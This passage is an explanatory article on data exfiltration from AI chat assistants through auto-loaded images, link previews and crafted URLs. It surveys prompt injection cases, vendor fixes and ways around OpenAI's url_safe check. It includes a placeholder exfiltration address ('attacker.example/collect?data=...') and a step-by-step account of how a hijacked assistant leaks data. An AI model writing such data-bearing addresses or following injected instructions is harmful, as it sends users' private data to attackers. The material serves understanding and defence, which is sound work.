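# How AI chat interfaces leak data through images, link previews and URLs

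## How can displaying an answer send private data to a stranger?

AI chat assistants such as ChatGPT, Microsoft Copilot, Claude and Gemini produce text, which the software around them displays as paragraphs, tables, clickable links and pictures. To show a picture, the software usually has to request it from a server on the internet. An attacker who can influence what the assistant writes can get it to write a picture address that points to the attacker's server and contains the user's private data. When the software requests the picture, it sends that data to the attacker.

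In security, exfiltration means moving private data to someone who should not have it. *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a 2026 post by security researcher Johann Rehberger on Embrace The Red, describes this kind of leak as one of the most common security flaws in AI applications. Rehberger first reported it to OpenAI, the maker of ChatGPT, in early 2023.

In the simplest version of the attack, the model makes no network requests and only writes text. This section therefore has to explain why a model would write what a stranger wants, and why writing an address can be enough to send data.

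### Why models follow instructions from strangers

A language model composes its answer from its context, which is all the text the software gives it. This includes the developer's standing instructions, the user's question, the earlier conversation and anything the assistant has looked up, such as a web page or last week's email. The software developer Simon Willison (2025) points out in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that all of this is "glued together into a sequence of tokens", the word fragments that a model processes. The model cannot reliably rank those fragments by who wrote them.

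An agent is an AI model that can read data and use tools on a user's behalf, for example by searching a mailbox or opening a web page. Agents make the problem worse because they fill their context with a lot of text that the user has never looked at.

*Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced indirect prompt injection, the attack that exploits this. Greshake's team hid instructions in material that somebody else's assistant would later read, and Microsoft's Bing Chat and other systems followed them. Earlier work on manipulating chatbots had assumed that the attacker was the person typing. An attacker can publish a web page and wait for a search to turn it up, or email the victim. The instructions can be in white text on a white background or in a plain text file (Microsoft, 2025). According to *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in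 LLM-Based AI Agents* (2026), the attacker needs no access to the conversation, only the ability to put content somewhere the agent will read it. An agent following such instructions is a hijacked agent.

This problem resembles SQL injection, an old attack in which somebody types a database command into a web form and the database runs it. Programmers prevent that by sending commands and data separately, so that the database can never run data as a command. David C's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, which the UK's National Cyber Security Centre published in December 2025, argues that language models have no equivalent fix. A model has no separate slots for data and instructions, and predicts the next token from all the tokens so far. Developers can mark some of the text as "data", but the underlying technology has no such distinction.

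In the same post, David C prefers a different comparison, the "confused deputy", which is a high-privilege program that someone with lower privileges tricks into acting for them. Programmers can fix an ordinary confused deputy, but he calls language models "inherently confusable" and thinks nobody may ever fully fix them, so designers should limit what a confused model can do.

### What a web address gives away

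Chat assistants commonly format their answers in Markdown. According to MacFarlane's *CommonMark Spec*, John Gruber developed this plain text format in 2004, along with a program that converts it to HTML, the language of web pages. A Markdown link consists of a label and an address. *8.17 Images*, a section of the manual for the document converter Pandoc, explains that an exclamation mark directly before a link turns it into an image. A language model can therefore include an image in its answer just by writing a line of text.

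The renderer is the software that turns the model's text output into what the user sees, including images, links and diagrams. The output contains only an image's address, so the renderer requests the picture from the server at that address. This is an automatic fetch, meaning a request the software makes without the user asking. Developers can block it with a sanitiser (code that removes unsafe elements before display) or a Content Security Policy (a rule that limits which hosts the browser may load content from). Without such protection, the renderer requests an image from an address an attacker chose just as it would from any other.

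A web address can also carry data. Searching a website for "knee pain" often leads to an address ending in something like `?q=knee+pain`. The part after the question mark, called the query string, can hold arbitrary text, and the server receives all of it. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) notes that websites commonly log the addresses that visitors request. A typical log line holds the requester's network address, the time, the path and query string, and a code for the result. The attacker gets this log line even if the server has no picture to send back and the image appears broken.

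Encryption doesn't prevent this leak. Miessler (2015), in *Never Send Sensitive Information in the URL, Even Over HTTPS*, explains that HTTPS, the encrypted form of web traffic, protects the whole address in transit, including the query string. But the receiving server has to decrypt the request to answer it. OWASP's *Information exposure through query strings in url*, guidance from a nonprofit that works on web security, lists places where query strings appear even over HTTPS, including web logs, browser history and the browser's cache.

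Both of those warnings are about honest websites, where the risk is that the wrong person later gets access to a log or a browser. When an AI assistant leaks data, the attacker owns the server and intends the data to end up in its log. HTTPS doesn't prevent this, because it only stops other people from reading the data on its way to the attacker.

Removing query strings from every address would not solve the problem. Microsoft points out that the data can also be in the path or in a subdomain, the part of the host name before the main domain.

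### A leak in five steps

OpenAI illustrates the attack with a placeholder address, `attacker.example/collect?data=<something private>`. Nobody can register a real site under the ending ".example", which the internet's standards reserve for documentation. Spelled out, a leak to that address goes like this:

1. The assistant reads hostile text. A user asks about a web page, say, and the page contains instructions aimed at AI models.
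2. Private data is in the context, or within the assistant's reach. OpenAI's examples are an email address and the title of a document.
3. The model writes an address. It follows the page's instructions, puts the private item where the placeholder stands, and includes the result in its answer as an image or a link. A hijacked agent with a browsing tool can pass the address to the tool instead.
4. Software fetches the address.
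5. The server at attacker.example logs the request, and the attacker reads the value in the log.

The last two steps involve ordinary web software working correctly. It would fetch a harmless chart from a news site in the same way. The user may notice nothing, because the request can happen in the background and the visible answer need not contain anything sensitive.

The third step can fail on its own, because the model must find the right piece of data and put it in the right place. *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* (2025) accounts for this in how it scores an attack that asked a report-writing agent called AIRA to include an image and a link with gaps for the user's details. The attack got half marks if the link was displayed with the gaps unfilled, since a link without data in it leaks little. AIRA's report displayed the links in a section of their own.

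### Who makes the request, and who can see it

"Software fetches the address" covers three different situations, and anyone trying to notice or investigate a leak needs to tell them apart.

The fetch may come from the user's own browser or app, as when a chat window loads an image. The attacker's log then shows the user's network address as well as the data. An employer might spot the leak, because its network equipment can record a connection to an unfamiliar host, although encryption hides the query string unless the employer decrypts staff traffic. Security software on the user's computer may record more. The AI vendor holds the text of the answer, including the image's URL, but the image request goes straight from the user's device to the attacker.

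The fetch may also come from a messaging platform's servers. Many people now talk to agents inside apps such as Slack and Telegram. When a message contains a link, these platforms fetch the page to show a preview with its title and picture, which developers also call unfurling. *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*, by the security company PromptArmor, explains that a preview makes the same type of request as a click, without anyone clicking. PromptArmor set up a test site that records these visits, including those from Slack's and Telegram's preview bots. The attacker's log shows the platform's bot as the visitor. The platform can see the request, but the employer can see only normal traffic to a messaging app on its network.

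Finally, the AI vendor's servers may make the request, typically because an agent has opened a web page with a browsing tool. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) discusses one such attack, on ChatGPT's Deep Research feature, and notes that the outgoing request could be absent from both the user's browser and the employer's monitoring of staff computers. The attacker sees a request from the vendor's software. For example, when Willison had the Claude app fetch a test page in September 2025, the request carried the name "Claude-User". The vendor is therefore the only party besides the attacker that is well placed to observe the leak, and it is also the best placed to prevent it. OpenAI now has its agents automatically load only addresses that an independent crawler has already found on the public web.

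An attacker loses little when a bot's network address replaces the user's in the log. The query string can carry the user's name.

Security writers also sort these leaks by what the victim has to do. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), a case study of a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, uses "zero-click" for an attack that needs no user action beyond the assistant processing the attacker's email. The term is slightly misleading, because the victim usually does something, such as asking for a summary of recent messages. But the victim never opens, clicks or approves anything from the attacker. A one-click leak requires the victim to click a link once. Images that load by themselves, link previews and an agent's own page visits are all zero-click. An ordinary link in a chat window is one-click, but the same link becomes zero-click if the agent posts it in an app that makes previews. The label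 therefore depends on both the model's output and the software that displays it.

### The lethal trifecta

An AI system is vulnerable to this sort of theft when it has access to private data, takes in content that an attacker could have written, and can communicate with the outside world. In June 2025 Willison named this combination the "lethal trifecta". Removing any one of the three prevents the theft, but a hijacked agent may still do other harm, such as deleting files or giving false answers.

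People tend to recognise the first two ingredients but more easily miss the third, a way to send data out. An assistant that summarises email has the first two, because the inbox is private and anybody can write to it. If its answers appear in a window that loads images from any address, the renderer can send data out, even when the assistant itself cannot send email, post messages or browse the web. A company might reasonably overlook this and conclude that such an assistant cannot leak anything. Willison counts loading an image as external communication, and even offering the user a link to click. In June 2024, a year before coining the phrase, he had already written that a chat interface with private data, untrusted data and support for Markdown images has an exfiltration vulnerability.

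Data can also leak when a message is displayed outside a chat window. In May 2026, Willison noted a report of data leaking through images in messages that Microsoft Copilot Cowork sent to the user's own inbox. He did not mention a fix in that entry.

Willison generally favours designs that remove the assistant's ability to send data out, because an assistant without access to private data or outside content would be much less useful. OpenAI's Lockdown Mode, which began reaching ordinary ChatGPT accounts in June 2026, takes this approach. It limits outgoing requests but does not try to keep hostile instructions out of what ChatGPT reads.

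The other hope is that models will stop obeying instructions from strangers, and recent evidence is more encouraging. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* cites benchmarks in which injected instructions succeeded more than 60% of the time across leading models. In July 2026, by contrast, Trajectory Labs ran 720 injection attempts for Anthropic against three Claude models in the coding tool Claude Code, and none worked. The tool was in "auto mode", where software rather than the user approves the agent's actions. Willison, who reported the result in August, wanted more independent confirmation and doubted that auto mode could catch a malicious software package that the agent seemed to have a routine reason to run. The test also covered a coding tool whose actions are checked. Such a check would not normally examine a chat window loading an image, so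 one mistake by the model there is enough to send the data.

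## Why does the display layer belong in the threat model?

A threat model is a security team's account of who might attack a system, what they want and which parts of the system they could use. For an AI assistant, the obvious parts to list are the model, the data it can read and the tools it can call. The renderer, which is the software that displays the answer, also belongs on the list, but it is easy to overlook because it seems to run only after everything important has happened. The case for including it rests on both what models write and what renderers can do.

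### Displaying text as an action

A model that reads untrusted text can produce untrusted output because, as *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (2026) notes, many applications cannot reliably separate instructions from data. If a stranger's email is in the context, the stranger may have influenced any word of the answer. Nearly all inbox summaries are harmless, but the software that receives a summary can't distinguish a harmless one from one that an attacker shaped. OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* therefore advises developers to treat the model like any other user and to check its output before another component acts on it.

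A model without tools only produces text. The renderer, however, runs on the user's device, perhaps inside a company network, on a page where the user has already logged in. It therefore has network access and the user's session, the logged-in state that lets the page load private conversations without asking for a password again.

An image leak needs only the browser's network access. The attacker's server doesn't receive the chat site's login cookies, but the attacker doesn't need them because the model has already written the private data into the image's URL. If an attacker gets a script to run on the page, the script can also use the user's session to do much of what the user could do there.

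Together, these claims mean that displaying an answer has security consequences. A security reviewer would immediately object to a tool that let an assistant send any text to any server without asking the user. A renderer that loads images from any host gives the assistant much the same ability, but it doesn't appear on any list of tools.

### Precedents in email and on the web

Email marketers used remote images to collect information long before chat assistants existed. A tracking pixel is a tiny, usually invisible image whose address contains a code unique to the recipient. When the mail program loads the image, the sender learns that the recipient opened the message, along with the time and the network address.

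Outlook 2003 blocked remote images by default. In December 2013, Gmail began loading them through Google's own servers, which hides the reader's network address from the sender but not the code in the image's URL, because Google's server has to request the full URL to get the image. A chat window that fetched its images through the vendor's servers would have the same limitation.

A tracking pixel reveals fairly little, because the sender writes its address in advance and can include only what they already know. *Efail* (Poddebniak, Dresen and colleagues, 2018) describes attacks that removed this limit for email encrypted with OpenPGP or S/MIME, the two main standards. The attacker takes an encrypted message captured earlier, perhaps years ago, and sends it inside a new email to someone who can decrypt it. The victim's mail program decrypts the old message and treats the result as part of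 a web page that the attacker has partly written. The decrypted text becomes part of an address, and when the program requests that address, the attacker's server receives the text. The team found such leaks in 23 of the 35 S/MIME programs they tested and 10 of the 28 OpenPGP programs.

CERT-EU's *Security Advisory 2018-014* (2018) explained that the Efail attack on encrypted email depended on a mail program that rendered HTML and allowed downloads from external websites. The attacker did not need to steal a key. The abstract of Black Hat's conference talk *Efail* (2018) suggests that people had trusted email encryption, despite its outdated cryptography, because they thought of email as non-interactive, meaning that an attacker could send a message but could not get the victim's software to respond. However, a mail program does respond when it loads remote content. An assistant that only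 summarises documents can look non-interactive in the same way.

EFAIL is the closest precedent for the AI leak, because in both cases software mixes a stranger's text with private text and a renderer then acts on the result. The AI version gives the attacker more choice over what to take, because a hijacked agent can search for a particular item or summarise a long conversation before writing the URL, whereas EFAIL mechanically moved a message's text into one.

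Cross-site scripting, or XSS, is an older problem in which a website displays a stranger's text in a way that lets it run as code. For example, someone posts a comment containing a script, the site includes the comment in its page, and visitors' browsers run the script as if it were the site's own. Web developers prevent this by making the page show the comment as plain text, rather than by trying to stop strangers from typing scripts.

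Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026), in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, apply this reasoning to language models. They argue that when XSS happens through a model, the flaw "remains the unsafe rendering of untrusted content". The model usually carries the attacker's influence to a weakness the application already had, rather than creating a new one. In one of their examples, since patched, DeepSeek's chat site treated HTML from the model as live content, so a script in an answer could read the token that kept the user logged in.

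Their own experiment tested a different web flaw, server-side request forgery, in which an attacker gets a server to make requests on the attacker's behalf. They built a small application called TicketOracle and ran five attack scenarios against seven models. How often the attacks worked varied substantially by model, but they conclude that the weakness lies in the application. This supports their general argument, but they did not measure rendering, so their case about display relies on the analogy and on examples such as DeepSeek's.

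The analogy with XSS can also mislead, because the usual XSS defences stop scripts and a leaking image contains none. A sanitiser that removes scripts but keeps ordinary images will let the leaking image through, so a developer can defend correctly against XSS and still ship a chat window that leaks data.

### How OWASP and MITRE classify the leak

In its ranked list of the ten main security risks for applications built on language models, OWASP calls the display problem "improper output handling", which means passing a model's output to other components without enough checking. One scenario in the 2025 entry closely resembles the leak in question: a summariser reads a web page with hidden instructions, takes sensitive content from the user's conversation and sends it to an attacker's server. The remedies fit that scenario less well. For example, OWASP recommends a strict Content Security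 Policy, but as a defence against XSS, and a policy that restricts only scripts still lets images load.

The 2026 edition, published in August, addresses the gap directly. According to *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), an analysis by the web security company Invicti, the entry now names renderers that automatically fetch external resources as an exfiltration channel. Yet the entry, which ranked second in an earlier edition, fell from fifth place to tenth, the largest drop on the list.

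Invicti attributes the fall in rank to other risks becoming more urgent. A community vote determines three quarters of the ranking. The rest comes from 7,714 incidents in public vulnerability databases, of which 6,639 had enough detail to classify. On the incident data alone, prompt injection would not have made the top ten. OWASP says this is because teams work hard to prevent injection, so fewer successful attacks reach a public database. That is plausible but hard to check, because the count would also be low if attacks were rare.

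A company shouldn't use these ranks to decide whether to examine its chat window. A single data leak through an image involves prompt injection (ranked first), disclosure of sensitive information (ranked second) and output handling. A team that worked through the top five and then ran out of time might never look at the renderer.

MITRE ATLAS, a catalogue of attack techniques against AI systems kept by the American nonprofit MITRE, has had an entry called "LLM Response Rendering" since April 2025. It describes the zero-click image leak. The entry's maturity is "Demonstrated", one level below "Realized", which is for techniques that attackers have used in real incidents.

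The ATLAS definition covers responses that "the user's client" renders, so it does not quite fit a link preview that a messaging platform's server fetches. D3FEND, MITRE's companion catalogue of countermeasures, also offers defenders little help yet. Its page on the technique, *LLM Response Rendering*, repeats the definition but lists none of the "artifacts", such as files or network traffic, that D3FEND uses to connect attacks to defences.

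Researchers have not settled on a category either. In *Shifting from Injection to Interaction*, Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues (2026) match OWASP's 2025 risks to entries in CWE, MITRE's list of software weaknesses. They describe improper output handling as an "output-to-execution" problem and put the CWE entry for XSS under prompt injection, whereas Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian treat XSS as a rendering flaw. An image leak doesn't execute anything, so it fits better in the survey's category for information disclosure and exfiltration. The category may determine whether a company sends a bug report to the people who train the model or to those who build the chat window.

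### Is prompt injection the real flaw?

Someone could accept these points and still see leaks through the renderer as a symptom of prompt injection. The model writes the URL that leaks data only because it followed an attacker's instructions, and fixing the renderer does not prevent the other harm a hijacked agent can do. OWASP's 2026 ranking, with injection at the top and output handling at the bottom, seems to fit this view.

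Injection is certainly the broader problem, but that is no reason for developers to leave the renderer as it is. The 2026 edition of OWASP's guidance tells them, "Stop trying to build a model that cannot be fooled." Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* reports that OWASP advises developers to assume injection will eventually succeed and to constrain what the model's outputs can reach.

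*Analyzing AI Application Threat Models*, by the security company NCC Group, describes "soft" controls, such as a second model that watches the first, as useful additions but inadequate as the main defence. A renderer that refuses to load images from unknown hosts applies the same rule no matter how thoroughly an attacker has manipulated the model.

EFAIL prompted a similar argument. Sophos, a security company, blamed loose encryption standards rather than bugs in mail programs. The researchers also wanted new standards, but as a long-term remedy. Their immediate advice on the EFAIL website was to decrypt messages in a separate application and turn off HTML rendering, which users could do without waiting for a new standard.

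The objection would be stronger if models became almost impossible to hijack. The Claude Code test in which all 720 injection attempts failed is a step in that direction. But zero successes in 720 independent attempts is still compatible with a true success rate as high as about 0.4%, at the 95% confidence level. At that rate, an attacker who got hostile emails in front of 10,000 assistants would hijack about 40 of them. The real rate could be far lower, or higher if attackers find better methods than the testers did. Either way, the number of leaks depends on the success rate multiplied by the chance that the data can get out, and a developer can reduce that chance without knowing the success rate.

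### Does an agent have other exits anyway?

Another objection is that an attacker doesn't need an image if the agent can send email, run code or browse the web, because the attacker can use those abilities to steal the data instead. MITRE ATLAS gives this some support, since it rates exfiltration through an agent's tools as "Realized" and response rendering only as "Demonstrated". Blocking images in a product with such an agent might just push attackers towards its tools.

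Blocking leaks through the display layer does leave other channels open. The EFAIL researchers told people to turn HTML off, though they also warned that mail programs had other channels unrelated to HTML, which were harder to exploit. In the slides for a December talk, *Attacking end-to-end email encryption*, Poddebniak, Dresen and colleagues (2018) offered a crate of the soft drink Club Mate to the first person to leak an encrypted email's text through an attachment, such as a PDF or Word file, instead of HTML.

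If an assistant has no tool that can send data out, the display layer may be the only way for data to leak. Even in a product with powerful tools, it needs separate attention. A tool call normally passes through the developer's code, where the developer can add a check, a log entry or a request for the user's approval. The browser loads images by itself, without any of these safeguards unless the developer adds them. A company could therefore require approval for every tool call and still leak data through an image. A threat model should list every way data can leave, including the display layer.

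### Why vendors disagree about whether it is a vulnerability

In 2023 Rehberger found essentially the same image leak in several companies' products. Microsoft fixed it in Bing Chat and Anthropic in Claude, but OpenAI at first declined to fix it in ChatGPT.

This leak is difficult to address partly because the model and the renderer each behave normally. Security teams usually look for a defect that lets someone cross a boundary the software should enforce, so a vendor that examines each part separately can conclude that there is nothing to fix. The leak becomes visible when the vendor examines the whole product and sees a user's private data arriving on a stranger's server. Examining the whole product is also more useful to the user, who never agreed to send the data and cannot repair either part.

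Severity scores have the same problem. The standard method, the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), turns answers to a fixed set of questions into a number from 0 to 10. *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* describes CVSS as suitable for conventional flaws but insufficient for agents, because a weakness in one component can cause harm to the user elsewhere in the system.

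Even within CVSS, reasonable people can score the same image leak very differently. They may disagree about whether the victim took part by asking for a summary, whether the damage extends beyond the assistant to a separate system such as the mailbox, and how much data gets out. The scores below come from the version 3.1 formula, for an attack that works over the internet, needs no account, is not complex and only exposes data.

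| How the scorer answers | Score |
|---|---|
| No user interaction, serious data loss, damage extends to another system | 8.6 (high) |
| No user interaction, serious data loss, damage stays within the assistant | 7.5 (high) |
| User interaction needed, serious data loss, damage stays within the assistant | 6.5 (medium) |
| User interaction needed, limited data loss, damage stays within the assistant | 4.3 (medium) |

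CVSS also has no good way to represent how likely the model is to follow the attacker's instructions. A scorer can rate the attack's complexity as low or high, and changing it to high lowers the 7.5 in the table to 5.9. But the formula gives the same result whether the model follows the instructions half the time or once in a thousand attempts.

A display flaw's severity score can go out of date even if the renderer doesn't change. In Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground*, Rehberger rated an image leak in that product as only medium severity. The playground, a site for trying out models, could not yet bring outside content into the conversation by itself, so an attacker mostly had to rely on a user pasting in hostile text. Microsoft fixed the flaw anyway, about seven weeks after the report. If Microsoft had left the flaw and later connected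 the playground to email, the leak would have become much more serious. Vendors should therefore rescore known display flaws whenever they give the assistant a new source of data.

Bug bounty programmes pay outsiders for reporting flaws, and their rules define which flaws qualify. OpenAI had no such programme in early 2023, and Rehberger recalls on Embrace The Red that he had to email his report. A programme that excludes prompt injection as mere model behaviour could reject an image leak because the attack starts with prompt injection. A better test is whether private data reached a server that the user had not chosen. A company using that test can pay for the report and fix the renderer without promising to solve prompt injection.

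These decisions also affect public statistics, because a leak that a vendor doesn't consider a vulnerability may never be entered in a public vulnerability database. OWASP took its incidents from such databases, so its count probably misses some display leaks for this reason alone.

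## How did auto-loaded images leak chats, and why does the flaw keep returning?

A chat window displays a Markdown image by converting it to an HTML `img` element with the image's address in its `src` attribute. The browser normally requests that address as soon as the element appears on the page. Many chat windows display an answer while the model is still writing it, so the browser can send the request before the user finishes reading.

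In 2023, researchers showed that this ordinary behaviour could leak conversations from several well-known assistants. Most of the vendors patched it within a few months, but the same flaw was still appearing in other products in 2026.

### The first reports

Roman Samoilenko found the leak in ChatGPT in late March 2023. *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* (Willison, 2023) described his version that April. A website added instructions to any text that a visitor copied from it. If the visitor pasted the text into ChatGPT, the model could write a single-pixel image with data from the chat in its address.

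Rehberger found the problem independently a few days later, as he recounts in *ChatGPT Plugins*. He reported it to Microsoft on 8 April and to OpenAI on 9 April.

Microsoft's Bing Chat could read the web page the user had open, which made the attack easier. According to Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, a comment or an advertisement on a page was enough to steal other data from the same page, along with a summary of the conversation. In Rehberger's demonstration, the hijacked assistant wrote the image only after two more turns of conversation, so a user who checked only the first answer would not have seen it.

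Rehberger wrote in his 2023 timeline that Microsoft told him about its fix on 15 June, but in a 2026 look back on Embrace The Red he dated the fix to May. Both could be right if Microsoft changed the product some weeks before telling him. The 2023 timeline is closer to the events and gives an exact day, so 15 June is the safer date for when the fix was in place.

After Microsoft's fix, Rehberger's attack stopped working, and he noticed that Bing Chat now had a Content Security Policy that let the page load images from only four Microsoft hosts. Bing Chat still needed those hosts for images such as those it generated on request. He could not tell whether Microsoft had changed anything else.

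### How a browser applies a Content Security Policy

The server sends the policy as a short piece of text along with a web page, and the browser enforces it for that page. In the current draft of the standard, W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the rule for images has the name `img-src`. A site that wants to load pictures only from example.com can send this line:

`Content-Security-Policy: img-src https://example.com/`

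Suppose a hijacked assistant on that site writes an image whose address is at attacker.example:

1. The renderer converts the Markdown to an `img` element, as it would for any image.
2. The browser prepares a request and classifies it as a request for an image.
3. Before sending anything, the browser compares the address with the `img-src` list.
4. The browser finds no match, so it blocks the request and reports a network error to the page.

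The user may see a broken picture, and the attacker's server receives nothing.

A site can have a Content Security Policy that does nothing to stop this leak. If the policy has no `img-src` rule, the browser uses the general rule, `default-src`, and if that is missing too, images can load from anywhere. An `img-src` rule can also list a whole scheme instead of a host. For example, `img-src https:` allows images from any HTTPS address, including the attacker's.

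W3C advises developers to use these policies as a backup for careful handling of input and output, not as a first line of defence against injected content. That advice suits cross-site scripting better than image leaks, because a leaking image is valid except for its destination. The policy checks the destination of every image on the page, no matter which component put it there.

However, the browser checks where the request is going and ignores what the query string contains, so a permitted host can still receive private data.

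### How other vendors patched the leak

Anthropic fixed the flaw in Claude by adding a "Show Image" button and loading the picture only after the user clicked it, according to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*. Rehberger had hidden instructions in the middle of a short biography of Albert Einstein and uploaded the file to Claude, which then wrote an image address containing a summary of his earlier messages. He reported this on 12 July 2023, and Anthropic closed the report on 26 July.

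The fix turned a zero-click leak into a one-click leak. Rehberger didn't think it was perfect. It depends on users being suspicious of a picture in an answer they asked for, and most people would probably press the button.

Microsoft used a sanitiser to fix the image leak in the Azure AI Playground, its site for trying out models. Rehberger reported the leak on 24 July 2023, and Microsoft finished the fix on 13 September. As far as Rehberger could tell, according to Embrace The Red, the software now inserted a space into the Markdown for an image. The renderer then no longer recognised it as an image and displayed it as ordinary text.

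A sanitiser can work on the Markdown, as this one did, or on the HTML that the renderer produces from it. Editing the Markdown is simple, but images get through if they use syntax that the renderer accepts and the sanitiser's developer did not think of. Working on the HTML avoids part of this problem, because the renderer has already converted the different forms of Markdown image into the same kind of element. In both cases the sanitiser protects only the output that passes through it.

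Google made the simplest change in Generative AI Studio, part of its Vertex AI service for developers. Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* explains that the studio stopped turning links and images into HTML. Rehberger had reported an image leak there on 30 August 2023, and Google accepted it as a security issue 22 minutes later. Google confirmed the fix on 19 October, when he asked about it, though he suspects it had been in place for some weeks. He thinks this is probably the best fix for security, especially in a product whose users don't need pictures. The same change would take more away from a general assistant, because people ask it for maps and photographs.

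Google also fixed a leak in Colab, its online notebook for writing and running code. Rehberger reported the leak on 29 November 2023, and Google closed the report in January 2024, according to Embrace The Red's *Google Colab AI*.

GitHub took longer with Copilot Chat, an assistant developers use in the code editor VS Code. According to Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat*, Rehberger reported the leak on 25 February 2024, and GitHub replied on 6 March that the bug was valid and that it was already tracking the issue. He asked about a fix on 1 June and received confirmation on 12 June, fifteen weeks after his report.

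Rehberger thought GitHub's fix had stopped Copilot Chat from displaying Markdown images, but Willison, in *GitHub Copilot Chat*, described it as blocking only images from untrusted domains. After another researcher's report in June 2025, GitHub disabled image rendering in Copilot Chat on 14 August, according to the security company Nudge Security. Image display had therefore either survived the first fix somewhere in the product or returned afterwards.

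Willison was keeping a list of such leaks by then. His earlier examples included Google Bard, Google NotebookLM, Amazon Q and Writer.com.

### ChatGPT, from "won't fix" to a URL check

OpenAI first responded that displaying Markdown images was a feature and that it planned no changes. Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities in LLM apps (Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude)* records the formal decision as "won't fix".

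This was easier to defend in early April 2023 than it became later. Without access to outside content, ChatGPT could generally see hostile text only if the user pasted it in. But OpenAI was introducing plugins, add-ons that let ChatGPT fetch material such as web pages and video transcripts, and Rehberger had warned that they would make the attack possible remotely. He then demonstrated this in *ChatGPT Plugins*, which describes a web page that took over a session through a plugin and obtained a summary of the user's earlier conversation.

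OpenAI began to block the leak in December 2023. Rehberger had shown the attack live the day before, with a volunteer as the victim, and his server had received the volunteer's conversation. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* explains how the new check, which OpenAI called `url_safe`, worked on the ChatGPT website:

1. The model's answer arrives in the browser and contains an image.
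2. Before displaying the image, the page sends the image's address to a checking service at OpenAI.
3. The service replies that the address is safe or unsafe.
4. If it is unsafe, the page doesn't request the image.

A check like this can cover the whole address, whereas a Content Security Policy mostly compares hosts. That may be why OpenAI chose it, since ChatGPT could keep showing images from across the web. It also gave OpenAI one central place to watch for attacks.

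The disadvantage was that nobody outside OpenAI knew how the service decided. Anyone can read a website's Content Security Policy in their browser, but Rehberger had to guess the rules behind `url_safe` by trying addresses. He tested 36 very similar image addresses on his own server, and ChatGPT displayed nine of them, for no reason he could see. Small amounts of data could therefore still leak, though more slowly and more visibly than before.

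Another weakness was that the website's own code called the checking service, so OpenAI had to add the same step to every other ChatGPT app. The iPhone app did not have it. Rehberger suggested moving the check to OpenAI's servers, where it would cover all the apps. He guessed that OpenAI had avoided this because it wanted to send answers to users without delay. Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, called the fix "half-baked", partly because the iPhone app was unprotected and partly because he expected attackers to find addresses that the check would accept.

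Researchers found ways past the check easily enough. Rehberger reported several to OpenAI in October 2024 and presented some at Black Hat Europe that year. The security company Tenable reported another on 10 December 2024, and OpenAI acknowledged the report the same day. Tenable had asked for news six times by 4 March 2025, and the problem was still unresolved when the company published *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025).

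OpenAI improved the URL check at least twice during 2025. The first improvement came after Tenable reported a different ChatGPT flaw on 15 April. According to Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface*, OpenAI's fix for that flaw included the improvement and reached all users by 30 April.

Some of the attacks Rehberger reported in October 2024 still worked after that. In Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*, he writes that he had repeatedly asked OpenAI about them over the previous month without an update. He published the attack but left out the injected instructions.

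Around August 2025, OpenAI strengthened the check again, which stopped the attacks Rehberger had demonstrated. He had also noticed that the check was no longer visible in the browser, which suggests that OpenAI had moved it to its servers, as he had recommended in 2023. In November, however, The Hacker News (2025) reported a set of Tenable's findings about ChatGPT, including one that involved a trusted domain, which the check always accepted. OpenAI described its crawler-based check in 2026.

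OpenAI took more than eight months to release its first mitigation, and well over two years to release a check that stopped the known attacks. Bing Chat needed images from only four hosts, but ChatGPT's designers wanted to allow images from anywhere, so each version of the check had to separate safe addresses from unsafe ones using a rule that attackers could probe.

### The same leak in coding tools

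In 2025 researchers turned to AI coding tools, which can read a developer's files as well as the conversation. Those files often contain passwords and API keys, the codes that programs use to log in to other services. Developers also routinely ask these tools to look at code that strangers wrote, so an attacker can put instructions for the tool in a code comment.

Rehberger tried one of his old demonstrations on Amp, Sourcegraph's coding agent, and it worked. Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Amp Code* describes how a hijacked Amp could search files for secrets and then leak them through an image. He contacted Sourcegraph on 14 June 2025, and the company quickly fixed the flaw.

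Continue, an open-source assistant for VS Code, had a similar problem. The security company VerSprite tried two versions of the attack, described in its *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Continue*. In the first, the attacker's instructions were in a local file, and the leak needed no approval from the user. In the second, they were on a web page. Continue asked for permission to open the page, but then read a private file and loaded the leaking image without asking again.

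VerSprite reported this on 20 August 2025, and Continue's developers released a fix the next day. The extension now asks the user before loading an external image and restricts access to certain files. Such a question is more useful if it shows the image's full address, as PromptArmor's *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data* recommends, because users might notice their own data in it.

Other products have no known fix:

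- CodeGPT, another VS Code assistant. VerSprite reported a leak on 21 August 2025 and received no acknowledgement. A new version released six days later was still vulnerable, according to VerSprite's *Another Day, Another Leak*.
- HuggingChat, the chat app of the AI company Hugging Face. PromptArmor reported a leak on 1 December 2025 and published after getting no response.
- dify, an open-source platform for building AI applications, which veganmosfet, in *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend*, found vulnerable in December 2025.
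- Cline, a coding agent with more than two million downloads, which was vulnerable when Rehberger published Embrace The Red's *Cline* in 2025.

### Images inside diagrams

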